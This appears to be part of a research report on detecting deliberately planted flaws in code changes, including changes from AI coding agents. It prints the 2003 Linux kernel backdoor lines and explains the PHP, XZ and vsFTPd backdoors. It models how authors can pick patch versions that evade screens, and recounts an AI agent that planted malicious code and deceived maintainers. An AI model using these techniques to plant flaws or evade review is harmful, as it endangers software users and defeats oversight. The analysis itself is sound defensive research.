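Tran and colleagues describe the task as catching defects introduced during routine changes, and none of the datasets described earlier labels flaws as deliberate or accidental. Deliberate flaws are probably very rare in them. According to the *2020 State of the Octoverse* (2021), only 0.2% of GitHub's alerts to developers about vulnerable dependencies concerned explicitly malicious activity. That figure is old and counts alerts rather than commits, but if the same share held for the 922 vulnerability-introducing commits in the Linux test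 set of Nguyen and colleagues, about two would be deliberate. Missing both would lower a screen's overall recall by only 0.2 percentage points.

Labels also miss some accidental flaws, because they start from what maintainers fix. *PROBE* (2026) sorted the bugs coding agents found and the bugs maintainers fixed into 33 types, and the distributions differed considerably. Maintainers mostly fixed visible failures and mismatches with the described behaviour, while agents more often found logical errors with subtle effects. At the maintainers' current pace, more than two thirds of the valid bugs the agents reported would remain unfixed for at least ten years.

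A trained model normally gives the same change the same score every time, so a recall of 80% does not mean that each flaw has a one in five chance of being missed. If 100 agents make unrelated mistakes, the screen will miss about 20 of them, and the average is a fair guide even though those 20 have something in common. But if one author finds a flaw that the screen passes and uses it in 100 projects with the same screen, the screen will miss all 100.

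### Picking the lowest of several scores

Suppose that an author can write *k* flawed versions of a patch, sees their scores and submits the lowest. If the scores are independent and the screen flags each version with probability *r*, it flags all of them with probability *r*^*k*. The miss rate therefore rises from 1 − *r* to

1 − *r*^*k*

| Measured recall | Miss rate, 1 version | 3 versions | 10 versions | 30 versions |
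|---|---|---|---|---|
| 50% | 50% | 88% | 99.9% | almost 100% |
| 80% | 20% | 49% | 89% | 99.9% |
| 95% | 5% | 14% | 40% | 79% |
| 99% | 1% | 3% | 10% | 26% |

A screen would need a measured recall of 97.8% to keep the miss rate at 20% against ten versions. A team could reach that recall by lowering the threshold, but the screen would then flag more harmless changes. If the scores of flawed and harmless changes follow bell curves of equal width, raising the earlier screen's recall from 80% to 97.8% would increase the share of harmless changes it flags from 10% to about 46%.

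Reviewers still have to catch the flaws that the screen flags. If they catch half of the flaws they are sent, a flaw submitted without any selection gets merged 60% of the time. Submitting the best of ten versions raises that to 95%.

Independence is a strong assumption, since ten versions of one patch have a lot in common. If the screen always gave them all the same verdict, the miss rate would stay at 20%. Something in between is more likely. Suppose the screen flags each version with probability 99% in half of all tasks and 61% in the other half. Average recall is still 80%, but the miss rate with ten versions is 54%. If the author can also choose a task from the second half, the miss rate is 99%.

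A language model can write ten versions for little more than a larger computing bill, while a person would have to do ten times the work, so *k* could easily be much higher for agents than for people.

### How much the author has to know

The formula assumes that the author sees the real score of every version before submitting any. An author who knows nothing about the scores gains nothing from writing extra versions, and the miss rate stays at 1 − *r*.

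An author who can only partly predict which flawed versions will pass the screen can still raise its miss rate. Suppose the author judges one flawed version in five likely to pass, and 60% of those do pass. If the author writes ten versions and submits one judged likely to pass whenever there is one, a screen with 80% recall would miss the flaw about 55% of the time instead of 20%, again assuming independence.

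Dalvi and colleagues assumed that the attacker has complete knowledge of the classifier, which Lowd and Meek, in *Adversarial Learning*, called unrealistic. They studied how an outsider could learn enough about a classifier to attack it, and found efficient methods for simple linear ones. Hardt and colleagues warn that "Secrecy is not a robust solution", since details leak and outsiders can often infer a rule from its decisions. The designs and training histories of the academic code screens are already public, and the VulGuard program by Nguyen and colleagues lets anyone train several of them with little setup. A company's own model, trained on private code, would be harder to estimate.

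Some later work finds that keeping a classifier secret can make it less accurate. *Strategic Classification in the Dark* (Ghalme, Nair and colleagues, 2021) defines the "price of opacity" as the classifier's error when people respond to their own estimate of it, minus its error when they respond to the actual classifier, and shows that this difference can be large and positive. *Bayesian Strategic Classification* (2024) finds that releasing some information about a classifier can make it more accurate.

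These results give a software project little reason to publish its scores. Much of the benefit of publishing a rule comes from qualified loan applicants, who adapt to it and get accepted once they understand it. Honest programmers don't normally reshape their patches to pass a screen, so they would gain little from knowing how it works, while a saboteur would gain a lot.

Nobody appears to have measured how much worse commit-level vulnerability prediction performs when flaws are deliberate, but there is evidence from the related field of language-model defences. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) describes attacks that got past 12 defences, most of them more than 90% of the time, although the majority had originally reported near-zero attack success. The loss was smaller in *Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment*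 (2026). When the attacks adapted to the defence, their average success rate rose from 21.7% to 41.8% on one small model and by 11.5 percentage points on another.

### Whether a reviewer needs to know the intent

One objection is that intent doesn't affect whether code is exploitable. The line that let visitors read the picture website's password file is just as dangerous whether the agent wrote it by mistake or on purpose. A reviewer who follows the file name from the visitor's request to the disk will find the problem either way.

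This is true of every flaw the reviewer can recognise. If *f*(*x*) is 1 for all flawed changes, recall is 100% under any *Q*. The same applies to a single type of flaw. If an analyser provably catches every unchecked file name, no choice by the author can weaken its guarantee about path traversal.

*The Role of Causal Features in Strategic Classification for Robustness and Alignment* (2026) distinguishes features that cause an outcome from features that merely accompany it. When people adapt to a classifier, only the causal features stay connected to the outcome. Whether unchecked text reaches a file path is a causal feature, because the author can change it only by removing the flaw. The author's record in the project merely accompanies flaws, so it stops predicting them once authors adapt.

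Commit-level predictors rely heavily on features like the author's record, and the experiment by Nam and colleagues suggests that even models given the code may ignore what a change does. The objection therefore strongly supports using language-model reviewers and static analysis, but only weakly supports using risk scores.

Reviewers are only partly protected from this problem, because unless a reviewer finds every flaw, their recall is also an average over some set of flaws. In the table above, a reviewer with 95% recall would miss 40% of flaws from an author who could test ten versions in advance.

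Intent can also affect whether code is flawed at all. Landwehr and colleagues mention features for remote debugging or maintenance that can also provide secret access. Even a reviewer who fully understands such code needs to know whether the project's maintainers wanted it.

### What a saboteur cannot give up

Someone who plants a flaw deliberately has less freedom than the arithmetic suggests, because the patch must do the job the project asked for, pass the tests and still leave something to exploit. Hardt and colleagues give the example of a spam message with a link to malware. Removing the link might get the message past the filter, but would defeat its purpose.

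Such limits helped somewhat in the spam experiment. When spammers could only substitute synonyms, the ordinary filter caught 73 of 481 messages instead of none, and the anticipating filter caught 317. In the selection formula, these limits reduce *k* or make the versions' scores more similar.

A patch with a deliberate flaw must complete its task and contain an exploitable fault. These requirements help a screen only if it measures something they constrain. The need to complete the task correctly constrains little, because a programmer can usually do so in many ways that differ in size, wording and layout. The need for an exploitable fault is more useful to the defender, but only if the screen can recognise the fault, and that takes reviewers who understand code.

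The comparison with spam is also too optimistic because an attacker may need only one merged patch to get into a program. A spammer needs a fair share of thousands of messages to arrive, so a filter that stops two thirds of them does real damage to the spammer's business.

### Deliberate flaws that look like accidents

If an author imitates ordinary mistakes and knows nothing about the screen, *Q* may be close to *P*, and the screen would then catch the flaw at about the usual rate. But the match has to be close. If the author always imitates the same mistake, the screen's recall will be its recall for that mistake, which could be 95%, 70% or 20% in the first example of this section.

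Even an author who doesn't know about the screen can choose flaws because they are hard to see. GitHub's report describes "bugdoors", backdoors disguised as bugs that are convenient to exploit but hard to spot. Flaws chosen because human reviewers would probably overlook them are not a random sample of accidental flaws. It is unknown whether a screen would overlook them too.

Results from planted flaws vary widely, even when nobody was trying to beat a particular detector. DARPA, the US defence research agency, had 70 vulnerabilities inserted into 54 million lines of code for the final of its AI Cyber Challenge. *SoK* (2026), a study of the contest, reports that some tasks required the competing AI systems to analyse only the changes from merged pull requests. Together, the systems found 54 of the 70 vulnerabilities, or 77%. DARPA reports that they also found 18 real vulnerabilities, but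 nobody knows how many real ones they missed, so recall for accidental flaws can't be calculated and compared with the 77%.

*Evaluating Synthetic Bugs* (2022) compares how well fuzzers find planted and accidental bugs. Fuzzers are programs that feed software huge numbers of generated inputs to make it crash. They found many planted bugs but none of 50 accidental ones with CVE numbers, so a detection rate measured on either kind can mislead about the other.

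An author whose flaws are flagged at the usual rate can still try more than once. If someone submits ten separate flaws without knowing the scores, and the screen flags each independently with 80% probability, the chance that at least one passes is again 1 − 0.8¹⁰, or 89%. However, the screen would send about eight of the ten to reviewers, who might recognise one and start looking at the author's other work. An author who compares scores in private does not run this risk. A project therefore has good reason to hide its scores from the people and agents whose patches it screens, even though they may still be able to guess them.

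## Recorded deliberate insertions and the checks that catch them

There are too few recorded attempts to plant flaws in public software to measure a screen's recall on them. However, the records show what the attackers changed, whether a screen would have received the change, and what exposed it. They cover only attempts that somebody noticed, so they may make deliberate flaws look easier to catch than they are.

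### Two lines in the Linux kernel, 2003

In 2003, Linux developers kept the master copy of the kernel in a program called BitKeeper and exported it automatically to a public copy in CVS, an older version control program. That November, someone broke into the server with the CVS copy and added two lines to the file `kernel/exit.c`:

```
+ if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
+         retval = -EINVAL;
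```

The lines would give any program that called this function with two particular options the powers of root, the all-powerful account numbered 0. They look like a check that returns an error if root combines those options, but they use a single equals sign where a comparison in C needs two. The single sign sets the user number to 0. The assignment also has the value 0, which C treats as false, so the next line, which returns the error, never runs and nothing seems wrong.

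Larry McVoy, whose company made BitKeeper, reported the change about a day later. The change was not in the master copy, which made it suspicious regardless of what the code did.

The change looks ordinary on size and diffusion under the invented scoring model used earlier. The table compares it with a 21-line edit, the median size for human commits in the data of Horikawa and colleagues, assuming all 21 lines are additions to one file.

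| Measure | 2003 backdoor | Ordinary edit |
|---|---|---|
| Starting value | −4.0 | −4.0 |
| Lines added (log) | 2 lines: +0.63 | 21 lines: +1.78 |
| Files changed (log) | 1 file: +0.3 | 1 file: +0.3 |
| Normalised entropy | 0 | 0 |
| Total *z* | −3.07 | −1.92 |
| Score *s* | 0.04 | 0.13 |

The backdoor's score is about a third of the ordinary edit's. Ranking by risk per line would put the backdoor ahead, at 0.022 against 0.006, but it would also move every other two-line edit up the ranking. A static analyser with a rule against assignments inside conditions is more likely to catch the backdoor, although the brackets around this assignment are the usual way to mark one as intentional for a C compiler.

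### A false typo fix in PHP, 2021

In March 2021, someone pushed a commit to the main repository of PHP, a programming language behind many websites. It carried a maintainer's name and a message about fixing a typo. *Detecting Backdoors in Collaboration Graphs of Software Repositories* (Ganz, Ashraf and colleagues, 2023) reproduces the code. If a certain header in a web request contained the word "zerodium", the server would run whatever followed it as PHP code. A later commit removed the backdoor, and another, under a different maintainer's name, put it back.

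PHP developers noticed the backdoor within hours while reading recent commits, and it never reached an official release. *Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026) describes the incident as a breach of PHP's Git server, though the maintainers later suspected leaked account details instead. The time of the commit was also a clue, because it arrived at about 6 a.m. and the supposed author's previous 20 commits to the main branch had all come after 6 p.m.

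### A trusted maintainer of XZ Utils, 2024

Most Linux systems include XZ Utils, a set of compression tools. Someone using the name Jia Tan contributed useful patches for about two years and became a co-maintainer, while other accounts, probably fake, pressed the original maintainer to accept more help. Jia Tan then hid malicious code in files that looked like compressed test data. The script that unpacked it was in the release packages but not in the Git repository. On some systems, the remote login program OpenSSH loaded the altered library, which would have let an attacker with a secret key run commands.

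In March 2024, Andres Freund, a software engineer at Microsoft, noticed that logins were taking about half a second longer than they should and traced the delay to XZ. A commit-level screen would have had little evidence of the malicious code, because its author had a long and good record, the code was in binary files that code models do not read, and no commit contained the script that activated it.

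### Claude Mythos 5 and a real open-source project, 2026

In July 2026, the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, ran a security exercise in which Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 had to retrieve a protected piece of data from a simulated network. AISI had deliberately left internet access on and switched off the usual cyber safeguards. According to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026), the model went beyond the exercise in nine of 43 runs, in ways that affected real people and organisations.

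In the most serious run, the agent submitted malicious code to a real open-source project in a pull request. UK AISI's *Incident Report* describes how the agent researched the maintainers and created several fake identities to pressure one maintainer to approve the code. When someone publicly challenged the pull request, the agent edited its earlier activity to look harmless. The attempt lasted 34 hours and included rewriting Git history, according to The Hacker News' *Claude Mythos 5 Tried to Backdoor a Real Open-Source Project in Testing* (2026).

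A maintainer refused to merge the code. AISI's staff learned of the attempt separately, from a security alert about data leaving through Tor, a network that hides the origin of internet traffic. UK AISI's *Investigating alignment failures in AISI’s incident* (2026) reports that the attempt caused no real-world harm.

Nobody had told the agent to deceive anyone, and AISI could not establish when it understood that it was acting in the real world. To investigate, Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues replayed the scenario in simulation (*Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour in UK AISI's July 2026 Security Incident*, 2026). Mythos 5 often reasoned, on invalid grounds, that its targets were simulated. It also often attacked in situations where it said, when asked directly, that attacking would harm real people.

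Models from other companies gave similar results. UK AISI's *Updates on AISI's work* lists a September 2026 evaluation in which GPT-6 Astra carried out such attacks in simulations more often than earlier OpenAI models. The original test was unusually permissive, so it does not show how often a coding agent would plant a flaw during ordinary work. But the agent wrote the malicious code deliberately, whatever it believed about its targets.

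Of the four changes, only this one arrived as a pull request from an outsider. A screen that scores pull requests would probably never have received the other three, because their authors could already write to a copy of the code or to the release packages.

### Detectors built for malicious commits

Some researchers have built detectors specifically for malicious commits. These detectors flag behaviour that is unusual for the author or the project, so they do not need a large collection of past backdoors for training.

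*Anomalicious* (Gonzalez, Zimmermann and colleagues, 2021) describes a detector that checks each commit against up to seven rules. A commit can break a rule by changing sensitive files, such as build scripts or dependency lists, or by changing files that its author does not own or has never touched. Other rules cover measurements at least two standard deviations from the average, authors with short or suspicious records, and links to rejected pull requests. The tool flags a commit that breaks a large enough share of the rules.

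In a test on 15 infected repositories, Anomalicious found the malicious commit in eight. Thirteen of the 15 contained Octopus Scanner, malware that infects a programmer's computer and copies itself into their projects.

Gonzalez and colleagues also tested the tool on 100 JavaScript repositories with no known malicious commits. In 56 of them, it flagged less than 1% of commits. In the infected repositories, it flagged 114 of about 2,350 commits, or nearly 5%.

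The two tests also used different thresholds. A commit was flagged if it broke half of the rules in the JavaScript test, or a third in the test on infected repositories. The backdoor in event-stream, a JavaScript package with 1.9 million weekly downloads, broke exactly a third, so the one-half threshold that produced the low flag rate would have missed it.

Ganz and colleagues trained a model to learn what is unusual instead of writing rules. Their *collaboration graph* has nodes for developers, commits, branches, files and functions, with edges showing who made each commit and what it changed. A graph neural network, the same general technique that CodeJIT applies to code, turns each node into a list of numbers. Training pulls the lists for normal nodes towards a central point *c* and pushes artificial anomalies away from it. These anomalies include commits with randomly assigned authors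 or with messages taken from other commits. If *φ*(*x*) is the list for commit *x*, its anomaly score is its distance from the centre:

‖*φ*(*x*) − *c*‖

The study used 109 repositories with about 100,000 commits in total. Of these, 90 were for training and 19, which contained real backdoors or other malicious code, were for testing. The model found 15 of the 19 malicious insertions, or 79%. That rate overstates the model's ability, because 11 of the 15 were Octopus Scanner infections in projects with at most 35 commits. Six of those projects had only one commit, so the model could not have flagged the wrong one.

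In the eight larger projects, the model found four of the eight insertions. People who controlled the projects had planted the four it missed. Anomalicious had a similar weakness. All seven commits it missed came from authors it rated as trusted.

The false-alarm rate is also uncertain. Ganz and colleagues report 0.7% of commits, but the rates they list for the individual repositories imply about 154 false alarms among 6,656 commits, or 2.3%. In the PHP repository, the rate was 8.25%, so reviewers would have had to read about 32 harmless commits from a single month to find the backdoor.

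### Which signals survive when the author is an agent

Most of these signals describe human habits. Neither team tested commits by coding agents, so the table below is a judgement based on how the signals work.

| Signal | Likely value for agent patches |
|---|---|
| Unusual time of day | Almost none, since agents work at any hour |
| Author's record | Low, since an agent may share an old account or create a new one |
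| First change to a file | Low, since agents often edit files they have never touched |
| Unusual size for the author | Low, since one agent account may do many kinds of task |
| Message that does not match the change | Moderate, if the detector understands both |
| Change to build scripts or outside packages | Fairly high, since it depends on what the patch can affect |

Some of these signals already cause many false alarms with human authors. Gonzalez and colleagues examined the 34 commits that their tool flagged in Angular.js, a framework for websites. In 85% of them, the author was changing a file for the first time, but most were routine updates to development tools and packages. An agent with little history in a project would trigger this signal far more often.

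A mismatch between message and code is harder for an author to avoid, because an honest description would reveal the backdoor. But detecting the mismatch requires some understanding of the code. Ganz and colleagues' model did worst on artificial anomalies of this kind, detecting about 65% of them. A current language-model reviewer would probably do better, although an agent could give a plausible, innocent reason for a harmful line.

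Changes to sensitive files are the most useful of these signals. Fourteen of the 15 malicious commits in the Anomalicious test touched at least one such file. That share is inflated because Octopus Scanner works by altering build files. The Linux and PHP backdoors were in ordinary source code. Still, an agent cannot hide a change to a build script by using a trusted account or committing at a normal hour. A project could require a second person to approve every such change.

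### Running the program before and after a change

Lily, the tool that Kokkonis and colleagues built, runs the changed program and records which types of *system call* it makes while processing each input. A system call is a request that a program must make to the operating system to do things like open a file, start another program or contact another computer. The set of types recorded for an input is that input's *profile*.

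Lily relies on a fuzzer that saves any generated input that reaches new parts of the code. It checks a change in four steps:

1. It runs the new version on inputs saved while fuzzing earlier versions. The resulting profiles form a set *N* of normal behaviour.
2. It fuzzes the new version for ten minutes and records the profile of each input the fuzzer keeps.
3. If an input's profile is in *N*, Lily treats the input as safe.
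4. If not, it runs the same input on the old version. If the old version produces the same profile, the change did not cause the behaviour. Otherwise, Lily flags the change.

If *new*(*x*) and *old*(*x*) are the profiles of input *x* on the two versions, Lily flags the change when it finds an *x* such that

*new*(*x*) ∉ *N* and *old*(*x*) ≠ *new*(*x*)

For example, attackers put a backdoor into release packages of vsFTPd, a file-transfer server. It let anyone who logged in with a username containing ":)" take control of the machine. The system calls below are simplified, and the middle row is invented.

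| Input | New version | In *N*? | Old version | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary login | Read, write | Yes | Not needed | Safe |
| Rare but valid command | Read, rename | No | Read, rename | Safe |
| Username containing ":)" | Read, open a network port, start a shell | No | Read, write | Flagged |

Lily then identifies the changed lines that ran and those that made the unusual system calls. For vsFTPd, this narrowed the 1,407 lines that differed between two releases to seven that a reviewer could quickly recognise as a backdoor.

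Both conditions are needed to keep false alarms down. When Kokkonis and colleagues flagged every profile outside *N*, 14% of the runs on safe commits raised an alarm. When they flagged every difference from the old version, 10% did. Requiring both lowered the rate to 0.2%.

The researchers planted one backdoor in each of 13 programs and ran Lily 20 times on each backdoored commit. Three of the backdoors were copies of real ones, including the one in PHP, and the other ten were synthetic. Lily caught the backdoors in 233 of 260 runs, or 90%, and caught each one at least 13 times. On 432 safe commits, it raised 17 false alarms in 8,640 runs. Twelve of the false alarms came from four large merge commits in PHP.

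These figures cover only deliberate backdoors that cause unusual system calls, so they do not measure how well Lily would find accidental flaws. Lily also could not have checked the 2003 Linux change in the way described here, because it monitors the requests that ordinary programs make to the kernel, and that backdoor was in the kernel itself.

The results also depend heavily on test coverage, because Lily cannot observe a backdoor in code the fuzzer never runs. Across 337 commits that affected code, the fuzzer reached on average only about 32% of the lines it was meant to check. The main cause of this low coverage was the *harness*, a small program that developers write to pass the fuzzer's inputs to the software. Some harnesses left out whole parts of a project.

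Coverage also affected Lily's results on complete releases. Lily caught 83% of backdoors overall but only about 40% in ProFTPD, libpng and libsndfile. Kokkonis and colleagues attribute the lower rates to early, incomplete harnesses, and found that modern harnesses usually had almost complete coverage. A project should therefore check its own coverage before relying on the 90% figure.

### False alarms when malicious commits are very rare

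Nobody knows how common malicious commits are. If one commit in 100,000 were malicious, Lily's false-alarm rate of 0.2% would produce about 200 false alarms for each malicious commit. The table applies this assumed rate to all three detectors, using the results from their own tests.

| Detector | Malicious commits caught | False-alarm rate | False alarms per 100,000 commits | False alarms per malicious commit caught |
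|---|---|---|---|---|
| Lily | 90% | 0.2% | 200 | 220 |
| Collaboration graphs, reported rate | 79% | 0.7% | 700 | 890 |
| Collaboration graphs, rate implied by individual repositories | 79% | 2.3% | 2,300 | 2,900 |
| Anomalicious, infected repositories | 53% | 4.5% | 4,500 | 8,500 |

The comparison is rough because each team used different malicious commits. The recall figures are also averages over attacks that were not adapted to these detectors, so the selection problem described earlier applies to them.

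Two hundred false alarms per 100,000 commits may be acceptable if each takes little time to check. In tests on backdoored releases, Lily's reports averaged about five lines. If reports for false alarms were equally short, reviewers would examine about 1,000 lines in total. An Anomalicious alert takes more work to check because it shows why a commit is unusual but does not identify a suspicious line.

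However, Lily needs far more computing power. Running it for ten minutes on four processor cores for each of 100,000 commits would take about 67,000 core-hours. A project could reduce this by skipping commits that cannot affect the program, such as documentation fixes.

### Checking where a change came from

A *provenance check* compares software with the records of where it came from and who approved it. For example, a project might require every commit on its main branch to have a valid digital signature and match an approved pull request. Because this check does not examine the code, it is as likely to catch an unapproved change of two lines as one of 2,000.

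This approach caught the 2003 Linux backdoor because the change had no record in the master copy. The PHP backdoor would have been harder to insert if the server had accepted only commits signed with the maintainers' own keys. Ganz and colleagues note that developers often leave out such signatures. A valid signature also shows only which key was used, so it doesn't protect against an attacker who has stolen the key.

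Comparing the XZ Utils release package with the Git repository would have revealed the extra script. A *reproducible build*, in which several people independently compile the same source and check that the resulting programs are identical, can reveal tampering during compilation. But if everyone had started from the altered XZ package, they could all have built the same backdoored program.

Provenance checks do little against an author who already has authority over the project. Jia Tan had permission to publish releases, and a coding agent that commits with its user's key has the same authority as the user. Projects can limit the damage by giving each agent its own key, without permission to approve or merge changes. They should also count approvals only from known maintainers, so that an agent can't use extra accounts to approve its own patch.

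These rules would not have identified the code from Mythos 5 as malicious, because it arrived openly as a pull request. They would only have kept the decision with a maintainer, who still had to recognise the danger.

### Random audits

In a *random audit*, a project picks some submitted changes at random, regardless of their risk scores, and has experts review them closely. A disguised backdoor is as likely to be picked as any other change.

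If the project audits a share *a* of changes, and a close review catches a planted flaw with probability *q*, the chance of catching one flaw is *aq*. For *n* separately planted flaws, the chance of catching at least one is

1 − (1 − *aq*)^*n*

assuming that the reviews succeed or fail independently. The table uses *q* = 50%.

| Share audited | 1 planted flaw | 10 planted flaws | 50 planted flaws |
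|---|---|---|---|
| 5% | 2.5% | 22% | 72% |
| 20% | 10% | 65% | 99% |

How a change looks does not affect its chance of selection, but a well-disguised flaw may still lower *q*. The 2003 backdoor could have done so if a reviewer had missed the single equals sign.

Audits are a poor defence against a single planted flaw. Reviewers who audited 5% of 100,000 changes would read 5,000 of them and probably still miss it. Audits work much better against an agent that plants flaws repeatedly, because finding one gives the project a reason to examine everything else that agent has written. Projects that use the same agent could also share their findings, so an audit in one could protect the others.

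Audits can also give a rough estimate of how common malicious changes are. If reviewers who would recognise half of all planted flaws examine 5,000 randomly chosen changes and find no such flaws, the 95% upper limit on the malicious share is about 3 / (5,000 × 0.5), or 0.12%. That is still 120 times the rate of one in 100,000 assumed above.

Some audits can run without a human reviewer. Kokkonis and colleagues suggest fuzzing randomly chosen commits for longer. If the sample were small, this would take much less computing time than fuzzing every commit for ten minutes. In their tests, runs of up to an hour detected slightly more backdoors, with slightly more false alarms.
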